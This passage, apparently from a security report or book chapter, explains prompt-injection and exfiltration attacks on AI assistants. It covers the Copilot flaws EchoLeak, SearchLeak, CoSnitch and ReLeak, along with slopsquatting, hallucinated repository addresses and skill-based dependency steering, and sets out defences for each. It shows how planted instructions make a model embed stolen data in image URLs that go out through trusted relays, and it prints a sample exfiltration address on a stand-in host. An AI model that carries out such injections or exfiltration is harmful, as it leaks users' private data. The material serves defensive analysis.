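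Opus 5's most impressive result depends partly on added safeguards. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack succeeded in 129 browser scenarios when one program scanned incoming text and another blocked dangerous actions. Without these safeguards, the attack success rate was 3.7%. Even with them, a true rate of about 2.3% would be plausible after zero successes in 129 scenarios, assuming the scenarios were independent, and a higher one could be if they weren't.

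A low success rate per attempt protects a public chatbot less than it seems to, because attackers can keep trying. At 0.2% per attempt, the chance of at least one success in 1,000 independent attempts is about 86%. Better models are most valuable when an assistant needs wide discretion, such as when it browses the web, because a fixed rule cannot anticipate every legitimate action. TicketOracle's assistant never needs to contact the administrative service, so its developer can block those requests in code and has no reason to rely on the model.

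### Fixing the application

The most effective change is to have the tool accept a known event number instead of an address, as recommended earlier:

```
def get_event(event_id):
    if event_id not in KNOWN_EVENT_IDS:
        raise ValueError("Unknown event")
    return fetch(EVENTS_URL + str(event_id))
```

All five attacks then fail, even if the model follows the attacker's instructions. A planted review could still make the assistant describe a concert incorrectly or look up the wrong one.

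Tools that have to accept addresses, such as one that summarises web pages, need to check where an address leads before connecting. *AgentLens* (2026), which presents a tool for auditing agents, found that the popular coding agent Aider lacks this check. Aider asks the user to confirm before it fetches an address, but in the test it still fetched a cloud metadata address that the request had presented as a connectivity check. Confirmation helps only if the user recognises the address as sensitive.

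An attacker can register an innocent-looking name that points to 127.0.0.1, so the application has to look up the IP address behind the name and reject loopback, private and metadata addresses. It should then connect to the IP address it checked, without looking up the name again. Otherwise, the attacker can return a harmless address for the check and an internal one for the connection, a trick called DNS rebinding that a GCVE vulnerability record describes. OWASP advises against relying on lists of forbidden destinations because attackers know many ways around them. If the tool needs only a few sites, an allow-list of those sites with fixed protocols and ports is safer.

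A permitted site can also reply with a redirect, which tells the server to fetch a different address. If the server follows it automatically, the attacker can pass the first check with a public address and then send the server to an internal one. The application should refuse redirects, or limit how many it follows and repeat the full check for each new address.

Finally, the administrative service should require a credential that the assistant does not have. A request from the assistant's tool would then fail even if every earlier check had missed it. The service should also stop deleting records in response to GET requests, which by convention only read data. TicketOracle's tool could send only GET requests, so this change alone would have prevented the deletions, though not the disclosure of user records. Moving the assistant to a separate machine adds further protection, because a firewall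 between the two machines can block its requests, whereas traffic over the loopback address never leaves the machine.

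## Data stolen through images in Microsoft Copilot's answers

In most of the TicketOracle attacks, the attacker wrote to the assistant and could read the stolen records in its reply. An attacker who targets another person's assistant never sees the reply, so the attacker needs another way to get the data. If the application displays images, the victim's browser can send the data to the attacker when it loads one.

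### How a picture's address carries text

Many chat applications let the model format its answers in Markdown, a notation that uses asterisks to make words bold and brackets to insert links or pictures. An answer with a picture contains the picture's web address, not the picture itself. When the application displays the answer, the browser automatically requests the picture from that address, without the user clicking anything.

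The request includes the text of the address, and web servers routinely log the addresses that browsers request. Suppose an attacker owns the site collector.example and manipulates an assistant into adding a picture with this address:

```
https://collector.example/482913.png
```

The number is a login code from the user's email. The server doesn't need to have a picture by that name. The attacker reads the code in the server's log, and the user sees at most a broken-image icon.

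Nearly all browsers and servers accept addresses of 2,000 characters. If the site's name and other fixed parts take up 100, the attacker has 1,900 left for data.

| Private text | Characters | Share of the space in one address |
|---|---|---|
| Six-digit login code | 6 | 0.3% |
| Subject line of an email | 60 | 3% |
| 300-word email | About 1,800 | 95% |
| The same email in base64 | About 2,400 | 126%, so it needs two pictures |

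Base64 is an encoding that writes any data with letters, digits and a few symbols. It makes text a third longer but hides words such as "password" from a filter. The length is a minor obstacle because the data can be split across several pictures in one answer. A filter that looks for long or random-looking addresses also misses the login code, because ordinary picture addresses often contain longer numbers.

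Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* traces the technique, which is older than the cases below, to Microsoft's Bing Chat in 2023. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak'* (Willison, 2025) counts a dozen products with similar flaws and lists three conditions for them: access to private data, exposure to an attacker's text, and a way to send data out.

### EchoLeak: one email and three safeguards

Microsoft 365 Copilot is an assistant for Outlook, Teams and Microsoft's other office software. To answer an employee's question, it searches the emails and files that the employee can open and adds relevant passages to the prompt. Anyone can email the employee, so an outsider can put text where this search may find it.

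Aim Labs, Aim Security's research team, used this to build an attack called EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit* gives its severity as 9.3 out of 10. Researchers call such an attack zero-click because the victim doesn't have to open the email or click anything. The attack works when the victim asks Copilot a question that makes the search retrieve the email.

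The attacker can't know what the employee will ask. According to Willison, the email therefore contained passages on several likely topics, such as staff onboarding and leave of absence, and repeated the malicious instructions in each. The instructions told the model to take the most sensitive information from the material it had been given and put it in a web address. Microsoft had three safeguards that should have prevented this. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs from public reports how the attack passed each of them.

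Microsoft's injection classifier, a program that scans for planted instructions, was meant to stop the email before it reached the model. It would have flagged a crude message telling Copilot to ignore its instructions. But it could assess the email only by its wording, which the attacker chose. Aim Labs wrote the email as a request to its human recipient and never mentioned an AI, so it looked like ordinary office correspondence.

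Copilot was also meant to remove outside links from its answers, but its filter handled only the more common of Markdown's two link formats. The common format puts the address directly after the linked words, while the other puts a short label there and gives the address on a separate line, like a footnote. An employee who clicked a link in the footnote format would have sent the data to the attacker. The filter also missed images in the footnote format, so the attacker no longer needed the employee to click.

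Copilot's content security policy (CSP) should then have blocked the picture. A CSP is a set of rules that a web page gives the browser, including a list of the sites from which it may load pictures. Copilot's list did not include the attacker's site, so the browser blocked direct requests to it. However, the list was broad and included every address ending in teams.microsoft.com.

One of the permitted sites hosted a service that Microsoft Teams used for previews. Microsoft trusted the service as its own, but it fetched content from any address it was given, including an outsider's. Aim Labs pointed the image at this service and put the attacker's address, with the stolen data, inside the request. The browser allowed the request because it went to a permitted site, and the service then passed the data to the attacker.

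Willison calls the Teams service an open redirect, which would send the browser on to another site, whereas Reddy and Gujral describe a proxy that fetches the content itself. The proxy explanation fits better because browsers also apply a page's policy to the destination of a redirect, and would have blocked one that led to the attacker's site.

The email also told its "recipient" never to mention it, supposedly for compliance reasons, so Copilot left the email out of its answer. An employee who noticed a broken image would have had no reason to connect it with an unread email.

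### The EchoLeak timeline

Aim Labs reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft had started to fix it by April and finished in May by changing its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Both organisations published details on 11 June. Microsoft reported no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw. Its statement is somewhat reassuring because stolen data would have passed through a Microsoft service, and any records of the requests carrying that data could reveal attacks that customers could not have noticed.

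Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* reports that Aim Labs called EchoLeak the first zero-click AI vulnerability. According to Zenity Labs, a security research group, researchers had known about the individual techniques for one to two years. Aim Labs' contribution was to combine them into an attack that worked on a widely used product and needed no mistake from the victim.

### SearchLeak: a race against the filter

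A year later, the security company Varonis found another way to steal data through the same assistant, described in *SearchLeak* (2026). The attack exploits a vulnerability (CVE-2026-42824) in Copilot Enterprise Search, which finds emails, meetings and files within an organisation.

A link to the search page could include a query, as a link to a web search engine can, and Copilot ran that text as a prompt when the page opened. An attacker could therefore write instructions into a link and send it to an employee by email or chat. The link led to a genuine Microsoft site, so tools that block suspicious addresses were unlikely to stop it. After one click, Copilot searched the employee's mailbox and wrote an answer containing a picture whose address included the subject line of an email. In Varonis' example, the subject line contained a six-digit security code.

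Microsoft had a safeguard against dangerous HTML in Copilot's answers. It wrapped the output in a code block, which makes the browser display tags as text, but only after Copilot had finished writing. Like most chat applications, Copilot streams its answers, displaying the words as the model generates them. During streaming, the page inserted the model's raw output, and the browser acted on any tag it contained.

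Suppose an answer takes five seconds to generate and the picture's tag is complete after one. The browser requests the picture almost immediately, about four seconds before the safeguard runs. The code block then makes the final answer look harmless, but the browser has already sent the request. This is a race condition, a flaw in which the result depends on which of two operations happens first.

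The page's content security policy still restricted which sites the browser could load images from, but it allowed bing.com, Microsoft's search engine. Bing's image search accepts the address of a picture and fetches the picture for analysis. The attacker's image link pointed to this feature and included an address on the attacker's server that contained the subject line. Bing's server then requested that address, and the attacker could read the subject line in their server's log.

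The Next Web reports that Microsoft assigned the CVE number on 4 June 2026, and Varonis published its account on 15 June, after Microsoft had fixed the flaw. Microsoft called the flaw critical but scored its severity at only 6.5, while the US National Vulnerability Database scored it at 7.5, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026). Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* says the scores differ because the two assessments differ on whether the attack requires the user to act. Microsoft's assessment fits Varonis' account better on this point, because the victim has to click.

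### EchoLeak and SearchLeak compared

| Step | EchoLeak | SearchLeak |
|---|---|---|
| How the instructions reached the model | Copilot retrieved an email | A link supplied the prompt |
| What the victim did | Asked Copilot a question | Clicked a link to a Microsoft site |
| Why cleaning the answer failed | The filter missed one Markdown format | The browser sent the request before cleaning |
| Permitted site that the picture used | Microsoft Teams | Bing |
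| How the data reached the attacker | The Teams preview service fetched the attacker's address | Bing's image search fetched the attacker's address |

EchoLeak was an indirect prompt injection, so in principle Copilot could have treated the email as less trustworthy than the employee's question. This would not have stopped SearchLeak, because the attacker's text arrived in the place reserved for the employee's own request. Among older flaws, SearchLeak is closest to cross-site request forgery. An application can prevent this kind of attack by putting the link's text in the search box and waiting for the user to press Enter, although a user who doesn't read a long query may press Enter anyway.

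The two cleaning failures need separate fixes. A filter has to recognise both Markdown formats to catch EchoLeak's footnote format, and it has to run before the answer is displayed to stop SearchLeak.

The last two steps are almost the same in both attacks. Each relay is a form of server-side request forgery in which the attacker wanted a trusted server to contact an ordinary public website, rather than an internal service as in TicketOracle. The usual protection against server-side request forgery, rejecting loopback and private addresses, would have let both relays' requests through.

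### Later flaws and other ways out

EchoLeak and SearchLeak belong to a longer series of Copilot flaws.

| Disclosed | Attack | Product | What the victim did |
|---|---|---|---|
| June 2025 | EchoLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked a question |
| January 2026 | Reprompt | Consumer version of Copilot | Clicked a link |
| May 2026 | Unnamed | Copilot Cowork | Opened a message |
| June 2026 | SearchLeak | Copilot Enterprise Search | Clicked a link |
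| August 2026 | CoSnitch | Consumer version of Copilot | Clicked a link |
| December 2026 | ReLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked a question |

Varonis also discovered Reprompt, an attack that took the user's name, location and details from past chats. Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) reports that the attack kept running after the user closed the chat. It bypassed Copilot's safeguards by making the same request twice.

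The Copilot Cowork flaw involved images in the user's inbox rather than in the chat window. The agent could send messages to its user without approval, and Willison (2026) explains that opening one could load external images. An image's address could include a download link for a file in OneDrive, Microsoft's file storage service. Some of these links work without a login, so an attacker who obtained one could download the file.

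Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes another link that supplied a prompt, though this attack (CVE-2026-24301) did not use an image. Normally the prompt only filled the input box, but an undocumented setting in the link made Copilot run it immediately. The researchers learned of the setting by repeatedly asking Copilot why prompts could not run automatically, until one of its answers included the setting's name.

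The prompt made Copilot search connected services such as Gmail, put what it found into a web address, and ask for a summary of the page at that address. When Copilot's servers fetched the page, the attacker received the data. A content security policy could not prevent this because it governs only what the browser loads. Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on 18 August 2026. Varonis has seen no evidence that criminals used it.

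On 3 December 2026 the researchers behind EchoLeak, by then part of Cato Networks, published three more zero-click attacks. Simonovich (2026) presents them in *ReLeak* as a sequel to EchoLeak. In each attack, the instructions came from an unread email. One attack again hid data in an image's address and used Bing to pass it on. *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026) notes the similarity to SearchLeak, which had required a click.

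In another ReLeak attack, Copilot created a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing an address that included the stolen data. Microsoft's servers contacted that address while processing the file in the background, between one and eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the file. The last attack broke the network isolation of the sandbox in which Copilot runs code. Microsoft promised in its documentation that no network traffic entered or left this sandbox.

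According to *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026), Cato reported the flaws between 29 July and 20 August 2026, and Microsoft fixed the sandbox on 17 September, the file processing on 11 November and the Bing relay on 15 November. Cato knew of no victims. These dates show that a Bing relay was still usable that summer, after Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak. One plausible explanation is that the earlier fix blocked SearchLeak's route without stopping Bing from fetching image URLs in Copilot's answers.

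Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made". Both Cato and Varonis sell security products, and a series of flaws found by researchers doesn't show how often attackers steal data this way. But Microsoft confirmed and fixed the flaws, and they recurred even though Microsoft is one of the world's largest software companies and Copilot already had several layers of protection.

### Blocking automatic loading

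An application can show a placeholder instead of an external image and load the image only if the user asks for it. Many email programs do this because senders use images to learn when someone opens a message. A rule like this that covered every image address the model writes, including addresses on the company's own sites, would have stopped the zero-click version of EchoLeak. It would also have stopped SearchLeak if the page had applied it during streaming.

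Users have to make an extra click for each picture, which is a minor inconvenience in an assistant that mostly handles documents and a bigger one in an assistant that helps people shop for furniture. Some users will also click out of habit. Showing them the destination address helps only a little, because in both attacks it began with the name of a genuine Microsoft service.

Ordinary links can also leak data. If a user clicks a link whose address contains private text, the browser sends that text to the linked site, and a content security policy for images doesn't prevent this. The application can remove links to unapproved sites, but this makes answers harder to check against their sources. It can instead take links from its own search results and let the model choose among them by number, so that users keep the sources and the model can't add text to the addresses.

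### Cleaning the answer before display

Varonis recommends cleaning a streamed answer as it is displayed rather than afterwards. The simplest way is to wait for the complete answer, clean it and show it all at once. But this removes the main benefit of streaming, because if the model takes ten seconds to write the answer, the user looks at an empty screen until it finishes.

A better design cleans each piece of output as it arrives, before the browser renders it. A parser reads the Markdown, displays only a short list of permitted elements, such as paragraphs, lists and bold text, and shows everything else as plain text. Because a tag or link may arrive in two pieces, the parser has to hold back an incomplete one until the rest arrives, a delay users would rarely notice.

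Checking links after parsing would also catch the Markdown format that the filter missed in EchoLeak. A filter that searches the model's text must recognize every way of writing a link. The parser turns both Markdown formats into the same result, a link or image with an address, so a single check on the address covers both.

Cleaning answers causes users little inconvenience, but it depends on a correct list of permitted addresses. If the list includes a service that fetches any address for anyone, a perfectly cleaned answer can still leak data.

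### A narrow policy without relays

A shop's web page could limit its pictures with this rule:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://static.shop.example
```

The browser will then load pictures only from the page's own site and from static.shop.example. The second site should only store picture files. If it also has a preview service or an image search that fetches other addresses, it can act as a relay, as Teams and Bing did.

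Large companies find this difficult because one domain name often covers many services run by different teams. A team can add a fetching feature to a permitted site without knowing that another product's security policy depends on the site's behaviour. Varonis advises organisations to check their policies for such sites. Serving an assistant's images from a domain that has no other services is safer, because a new feature elsewhere can't reopen the leak.

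A policy can also permit one folder on a site instead of the whole site, but browsers ignore the folder restriction after a redirect. An open redirect inside the permitted folder could therefore lead to a relay elsewhere on the same site.

The relay can reject suspicious requests. Modern browsers label each request with its purpose, such as loading a page or an image. If people normally use a search feature by opening its page, its server can reject requests labelled as coming from an image tag without affecting normal use.

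For users, the main drawback of a narrow policy is that answers can't show pictures from most of the web. A travel assistant could still show photographs from its own collection, but not from a small hotel's website.

### Checking addresses on the provider's servers

Some assistants need to show images from many sites, so their providers fetch the images and pass them to the browser. This hides the user's IP address from those sites, but they still receive any text in the image URL. If a provider fetches every URL the model writes, its server becomes another relay through which stolen data can reach an attacker.

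Reddy and Gujral suggest a proxy that fetches pictures only from signed addresses. Before the model runs, the application takes picture addresses from a trusted source, such as a product catalogue, and uses a secret key to compute a signature for each one. The proxy checks the signature before fetching a picture. If the model adds a login code to an address, the signature no longer matches and the proxy doesn't fetch the picture. The model doesn't have the key, so an injected instruction can't make it produce a valid signature. The application must not sign addresses that come from incoming emails, and users lose any picture that the trusted source doesn't contain.

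A less restrictive check would allow an image only if its exact address appeared on the public web before the conversation began. This would block a new address containing someone's login code but allow a well-known photograph. Users would lose pictures from new pages and private sites unless they approved each one.

This check still lets a little data leak, because an attacker can encode information in the choice between known addresses. For example, an attacker could publish ten pictures in advance, one for each digit, and have the model request them in the order of a login code. A choice among *k* addresses reveals at most log₂ *k* bits, so each request reveals about 3.3 bits, and a six-digit code (about 19.9 bits) takes six requests. If the application allows only one picture per answer, the attacker gets one digit per answer. But with a million published addresses, a single request would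 reveal the whole code, so a provider also needs to detect sites that publish large numbers of nearly identical addresses.

One advantage of address checks over the other display defences is that the provider can apply them to every request its servers make, not only requests for pictures.

| Defence | EchoLeak | SearchLeak | CoSnitch | Main cost to users |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No automatic loading of pictures | Stops the zero-click version | Stops it if active during streaming | No effect | An extra click per picture |
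| Cleaning before display | Stops it if the check covers both formats and the relay | Stops it | No effect | Slight delay |
| Narrow policy without relays | Stops the zero-click version | Stops it | No effect | Few pictures from other sites |
| Address checks by the provider | Stops it if they cover links and relays | Stops it if they cover relays | Stops it if they cover page summaries | New and private pages may not load |

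These assessments come from reasoning about the published attacks, not from tests. So does a larger comparison by Reddy and Gujral. They expect a strict policy, signed addresses, an address allow-list or human approval to stop zero-click theft, but they don't expect labels on outside text and monitoring of outgoing data to be enough by themselves.

Their paper is less consistent about keeping outside emails out of answers to internal questions. They rate this measure as insufficient in their comparison, but argue in the text that it would make EchoLeak fail by design. The argument in the text is more convincing, because an email that never enters the prompt can't influence the answer. After EchoLeak, Microsoft reportedly added options to restrict Copilot's use of outside emails. An employee who turns them on loses some useful answers, such as a comparison of a supplier's latest offer with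 the company's budget.

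## Invented package names that attackers register

Most of the attacks so far depend on text that an attacker gets into a prompt, but an attacker can also exploit a mistake a model makes on its own. When models write code, they sometimes name a software library that does not exist. An attacker who publishes a malicious library under that name can reach developers who follow the model's suggestion.

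### How an invented name becomes an opening

Programmers build most software partly from packages, which are bundles of reusable code downloaded from public registries, chiefly PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. When a developer types a command such as `pip install requests`, a program called a package manager looks up the name, downloads the package and installs it along with any other packages it needs.

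A package can include a script that runs during installation with the developer's own access to files and passwords, so malicious code can run before the developer uses the package. *What is Slopsquatting?*, an article by Durnas for the security company Aikido, explains that these scripts typically steal credentials, such as cloud account keys. Some packages contain no harmful code but download it from another server during installation, so simple scanners miss it.

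Package registries give an unclaimed name to whoever registers it first. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) reports that anyone with an email address can publish on PyPI or npm, and that neither registry reviews first-time uploads. A command to install a package with an unclaimed name fails with an error, but once an attacker registers the name, the same command installs the attacker's code. The attacker never contacts the victim or manipulates the model, so the attack needs no prompt injection.

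Security researchers call this slopsquatting, after typosquatting, an older trick in which attackers register misspellings of popular package names. Nesbitt (2025), in *slopsquatting meets dependency confusion*, traces the word to a conversation in April 2025 about registries' logs of failed requests. These logs show which missing packages people are trying to install, so an attacker could use them to find the most valuable names, and a registry could use them to decide which names to block.

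### How often models invent names

*We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues, 2024), presented at the USENIX Security conference in 2025, was the first systematic study of invented package names. The researchers gave 16 models programming tasks in Python and JavaScript. About half of the tasks came from the programming Q&A site Stack Overflow, and a model wrote the rest. The researchers then searched the resulting 576,000 code samples for packages that did not exist.

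On average, at least 5.2% of the packages that commercial models named did not exist, compared with 21.7% for open-source models. The samples contained 205,474 different invented names. Socket, a software security company, notes that GPT-4 Turbo had the lowest rate, 3.59%, while two versions of CodeLlama invented packages in over a third of their outputs.

An invented package name is useful to an attacker only if it appears again. Spracklen and colleagues took 500 prompts that had produced invented names and ran each one ten more times. About 43% of the names came back in all ten runs, while 39% never reappeared. Only one model produced each of 81% of the names.

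These figures are for models from 2023 and 2024. In April 2026, Churilov gave the same prompts to five newer models and collected 199,840 answers. In a corrected version from November 2026, Churilov checked the suspicious names against the live registries.

| Model | Invented share of all packages named | Share of answers with an invented package |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 3.63% | 2.34% |
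| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4.09% | 2.75% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4.77% | 3.39% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 4.80% | 2.66% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 5.02% | 2.15% |

GPT-5.4-mini has the lowest share of affected answers partly because it gave no usable code for 31.5% of the prompts.

DeepSeek V3.2, the only open model in the test, performed about as well as the commercial ones, so the large gap between open and commercial models in 2024 has closed, at least for the best open models. It is less clear that commercial models have improved. The older method counted many correct uses as inventions because a Python package often has one name for installing it and another for using it in code. By that method, the same 2026 answers had invention rates of 4.6% to 6.1%, about the same as the commercial average in 2024.

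Djire, Barr and colleagues (2026) describe another source of overcounting in *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code*. Modules that come with a programming language do not appear in package registries, and counting them as invented packages inflated Python rates by up to 9.4 percentage points in their tests. Churilov looked for the same error and found none.

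The five models had 104 invented names in common, so one malicious package under any of those names could reach users of all five. Registry rules make some of these names unavailable. PyPI told Churilov that outsiders could register only 41 of the Python names on an earlier, longer list. But searching for names is cheap, since Churilov's answers cost about $1,160 to generate.

By November 2026, about six months after the test, people had registered 25 (1.1%) of the 2,282 names that the models had invented. At least one of the new packages contained malware. Churilov had accidentally published the list of shared names in April, but people registered those names no more often than the unpublished ones. The comparison was too small to detect anything but a large increase.

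### Cases outside the laboratory

The researcher Bar Lanyado noticed that models often gave the wrong install command for a real tool, with the invented package name huggingface-cli. Lanyado published a harmless package under that name, and it was downloaded 30,000 times in three months, Willison reports in *Diving Deeper into AI Package Hallucinations*. According to Durnas, Alibaba had copied the wrong command into the instructions for one of its public projects.

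A second invented name, react-codeshift, spread without anyone planning it. A model had apparently merged the names of two real tools, jscodeshift and react-codemod. In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, Eriksen, who works for Aikido, traced the name to a single upload in October 2025 of 47 AI-written skills, which are files of instructions that an agent loads for particular kinds of task. Developers copied the files, and 237 projects on the code-sharing site GitHub contained the name by January 2026. Eriksen registered it as an npm package on 14 January, before an attacker could.

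Eriksen's package received about 74 downloads on its first day, mostly from automatic scanners, and then one to four a day. Eriksen attributes the later downloads to agents following the instructions. This is plausible because an unused new package normally gets no downloads after the first day, but the count does not show whether an agent or a person ran the command.

Durnas also describes an npm package that did contain malware, unused-imports, whose name resembles that of a genuine tool, eslint-plugin-unused-imports. It still had 233 downloads a week in early February 2026. npm has since put it under a security hold, which replaces a malicious package with a placeholder. Aikido suspects slopsquatting but cannot prove it, and a person could easily shorten the genuine name in the same way.

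| Package | Contents | Downloads | What the case establishes |
|---|---|---|---|
| huggingface-cli | Harmless test | 30,000 in three months | People install a package under a name that models invent |
| react-codeshift | Harmless placeholder | 1 to 4 a day | Copied agent instructions can spread an invented name |
| unused-imports | Malware | 233 a week | Attackers have used a name that a model might invent |

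None of these accounts identifies a victim. In Churilov's data, at least 23 of the names that the models suggested had hosted malware before the test, until the registries removed it. It is uncertain what part AI suggestions played in spreading this malware, because the attackers may have chosen the names for other reasons, such as their similarity to popular packages.

### Invented addresses for projects and skills

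Models also invent addresses for other things that agents download. In *Beware of Agentic Botnets*, Spira, Cohen and colleagues (2026) call the attack that exploits this adversarial hallucination squatting, or HalluSquatting. For example, a user might ask a coding agent to download a project called librepods. Its GitHub address also contains the owner's name, which users rarely mention, so the model has to supply it. If the model guesses wrong and an attacker has registered the guessed address, the agent downloads the attacker's project.

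Slopsquatting puts malicious code in the package itself. In HalluSquatting, the download contains a prompt injection, and the agent may follow it by running commands on the user's computer. The attacker can therefore reach people without sending them an email or a document.

The researchers asked six models, without web search, for the addresses of ten popular projects from 2025 and five famous older ones. The models gave the wrong address in 92.4% of answers about the new projects and 0.9% about the old ones, probably because the new projects were missing from their training data. An attacker could have registered the invented owner's account name in 27% of the answers about new projects. Many of the other wrong answers named an existing account, so they could not be exploited this way.

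Spira and colleagues then tested complete attacks on six coding assistants, using harmless stand-ins for malware. The attacks succeeded in 20% to 65% of trials, depending on the assistant and its model, with 20 trials for each. All the trials used librepods, so the rates could be quite different for other projects. Attacks through invented skill names succeeded in 40% to 100% of ten trials on OpenClaw and two similar personal assistants.

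Web search prevented most of the mistakes. In one set of tests on the coding tool Cursor CLI, the agent gave the correct address 93.4% of the time when it searched first and 0.9% of the time when it did not. It skipped the search in about a third of cases, depending on the model and the wording of the request. Developers of such tools could make the search compulsory, although searching often failed when several projects shared a name. Asking the user to confirm the project's owner would help in those cases.

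### Skills that steer the choice of package

Liu, Hsu and colleagues (2026), in *Trust Me, Import This*, describe an attack they call dependency steering, in which the attacker publishes a skill that looks like ordinary coding guidance but favours the attacker's package. An attacker who can get a developer to install the skill does not have to wait for a model to make a mistake. The agent treats the skill as trusted and loads it again for later tasks, so one file can affect many projects.

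The researchers tested five open models on Python tasks. The largest, Qwen2.5-Coder-32B, named the package in 87.5% of answers on one set of tasks when the skill recommended it. The rate rose to 100% after a program optimised the wording. The lowest rate for any model and task set was 21%.

The 100% figure is an upper limit, because the program optimised the text only for success and did not have to make it look innocent. The attack stopped working when the skill omitted the package's name or heavily disguised it. A reviewer can therefore check a skill for unfamiliar package names before installing it.

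Automatic scanners were less help. Of eight scanning methods, two identified the skills as malicious, one rated them low risk and five found nothing. After the researchers used the reports from the first two scanners to rewrite one skill, one of those scanners no longer found a problem and the other downgraded its verdict from malicious to suspicious. The rewritten skill still steered the model in 65.5% of answers.

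The study measured how often models named the package, not how often an agent would install it, and it did not include commercial agents. Related attacks do not need to promote a particular package. *Harmless Yet Harmful* (2026) describes skills that make an agent invent packages more often, and *Package Hallucination Attacks on Coding Agents through Prompt Injection in Rule Files* (2026) reports high success rates for text hidden in coding-rule files.

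### Why checking that a package exists is not enough

The simplest defence is to check whether a package exists in the registry. This catches an invented name only while it is unregistered, when the install command would fail anyway. Once an attacker has registered the name, the package passes the check.

*Names Can Hurt* (Raj and Sahu, 2026) therefore adds a second layer to this check. If a package exists, a classifier predicts whether it looks suspicious from its name, its number of maintainers and whether it links to a GitHub project. If either layer flags a package, the system prompts the model again and eventually switches to a larger model. In 300 test runs, 76% ended with no flagged packages. This figure relies on the same detector, so a malicious package that the classifier missed would count as a success. The number of maintainers and the GitHub link provide 82% of the classifier's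 signal, and an attacker can fake both.

Of the detector's 179 warnings, 90 concerned packages already on PyPI, which Raj and Sahu present as low-quality lookalikes that an existence check would miss. Many of these warnings may be false alarms, because 54 of them concerned six names, such as pil and skimage, that Python programmers correctly use to import genuine packages that have different install names. The names are still risky in an install command, where the package manager will fetch whatever is registered under them.

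### Preventing the model from inventing a name

*PackMonitor* (Liu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) restricts which package names a model can write in an install command. A model writes a name in small pieces, choosing each from several possible next pieces. After `pip install`, PackMonitor removes every piece that could not lead to a name on a given list, so the model can finish only with a listed name.

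This method reduced invented packages to zero on all five models tested. Liu, Liu and colleagues report a delay of 0.05 to 0.3 seconds per answer, though their timings for CodeLlama show 0.58 seconds. The tests covered only `pip install` commands, so a model could still write an invented name in a file that lists a project's packages. The developer also needs control over how the model generates text, which providers of commercial models rarely allow.

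PackMonitor's guarantee also depends on its list of permitted names. If the list includes every name on PyPI, a package registered by an attacker becomes a permitted choice at the next update. Forcing the model to choose a real name may also lead it to the wrong package. A list of packages the organisation has approved would avoid the first problem and make the second much less dangerous.

Other methods make models invent package names less often. Retrieval looks up real packages and adds them to the prompt, and fine-tuning trains the model further on examples without invented names. The table compares the measured results, which come from different models and tasks.

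| Method | Invented share of packages before and after | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| PackMonitor, five models | 3.3–8.4% to 0% | Accepts any package on its list |
| Retrieval, eight small models | 29.7% to 18.1% | Raised the JavaScript rate by 12.7 points |
| The model revises its own answer, eight small models | 29.7% to 25.6% | Made some models worse |
| Fine-tuning, DeepSeek-Coder | 16.1% to 2.7% | Score on a programming test fell from 72.6% to 45.7% |

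Djire and colleagues, who reported the retrieval and revision results, also tested prompts that contained invented names. These prompts raised the rate of invented packages by up to 45 percentage points. Retrieval and revision were more robust to them than methods that only changed how the model selects words.

### Controlling what gets installed

An organisation can run its own registry that contains only approved packages and block access to public registries. A package with an invented name then fails to install, even if an attacker has registered it publicly. This works with any model and also limits malicious skills. However, someone has to review each new package, and developers have to wait for the review.

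A lockfile records the exact version of every package in a project, usually with a digital fingerprint of its contents. If the servers that build the software install only what the lockfile lists, an agent cannot add another package to the build unnoticed. But a lockfile does not show whether a package is safe. If a developer adds a malicious package to it, colleagues will install the same malware, so someone has to review changes to the file.

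Some package managers can also impose a waiting period, refusing releases less than, say, a week old. This gives registries and security companies time to find malware, including malware in releases of genuine packages, such as the unauthorised version of the coding tool Cline. The waiting period also delays urgent fixes unless developers make exceptions, and an attacker can register a name and wait until the period has passed. The studies compared here did not measure how well approved lists, lockfiles or waiting periods stop slopsquatting.

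These controls matter more when agents install packages without asking. Durnas recommends treating installation as a privileged operation and checking who published a package and when, because high download counts can be misleading. Turning off installation scripts also helps, but malicious code can still run when the developer's program uses the package.

### Expected exposure for a team

The published rates allow a rough estimate of the risk to a team without these controls. Suppose 20 developers each receive ten answers containing code every working day.

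| Step | Assumption | Number per year |
|---|---|---|
| Answers with code | 20 developers, 10 answers a day, 220 days | 44,000 |
| Answers with an invented package | 2.7%, the average in Churilov's test | 1,188 |
| Attempts to install one | 10% of those answers | 119 |
| Malicious installations, low estimate | 1 in 2,282 names leads to malware | 0.05 |
| Malicious installations, high estimate | 23 in 2,282 names lead to malware | 1.2 |

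The estimate ranges from one malicious installation every 19 years to slightly more than one a year. The low figure counts only the one package that certainly contained malware. The high figure adds 22 registered packages whose contents Churilov did not inspect, many of which may be harmless. It excludes two empty packages.

The team's size and habits are invented, and the 10% is a guess. The calculation also assumes that:

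- the team's questions resemble the test prompts, and its assistants do not search the web
- each affected answer contains one invented package
- people keep registering names at the same pace, so that the share after six months is also the average for the year
- every invented name is equally likely to lead to malware
- malicious packages stay available once someone has published them.

The last two assumptions affect the result in opposite directions. Attackers would prefer names that models invent often, which would raise the risk. Registries remove malware, which would lower it, and npm had already removed the one confirmed package.

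If the installations were independent, the chance of at least one in a year would be about 5% on the low estimate and 70% on the high one. In practice, installations would cluster, because developers on the same team ask similar questions and receive the same invented names. The expected number would stay the same, but the team would be more likely to have none or several.

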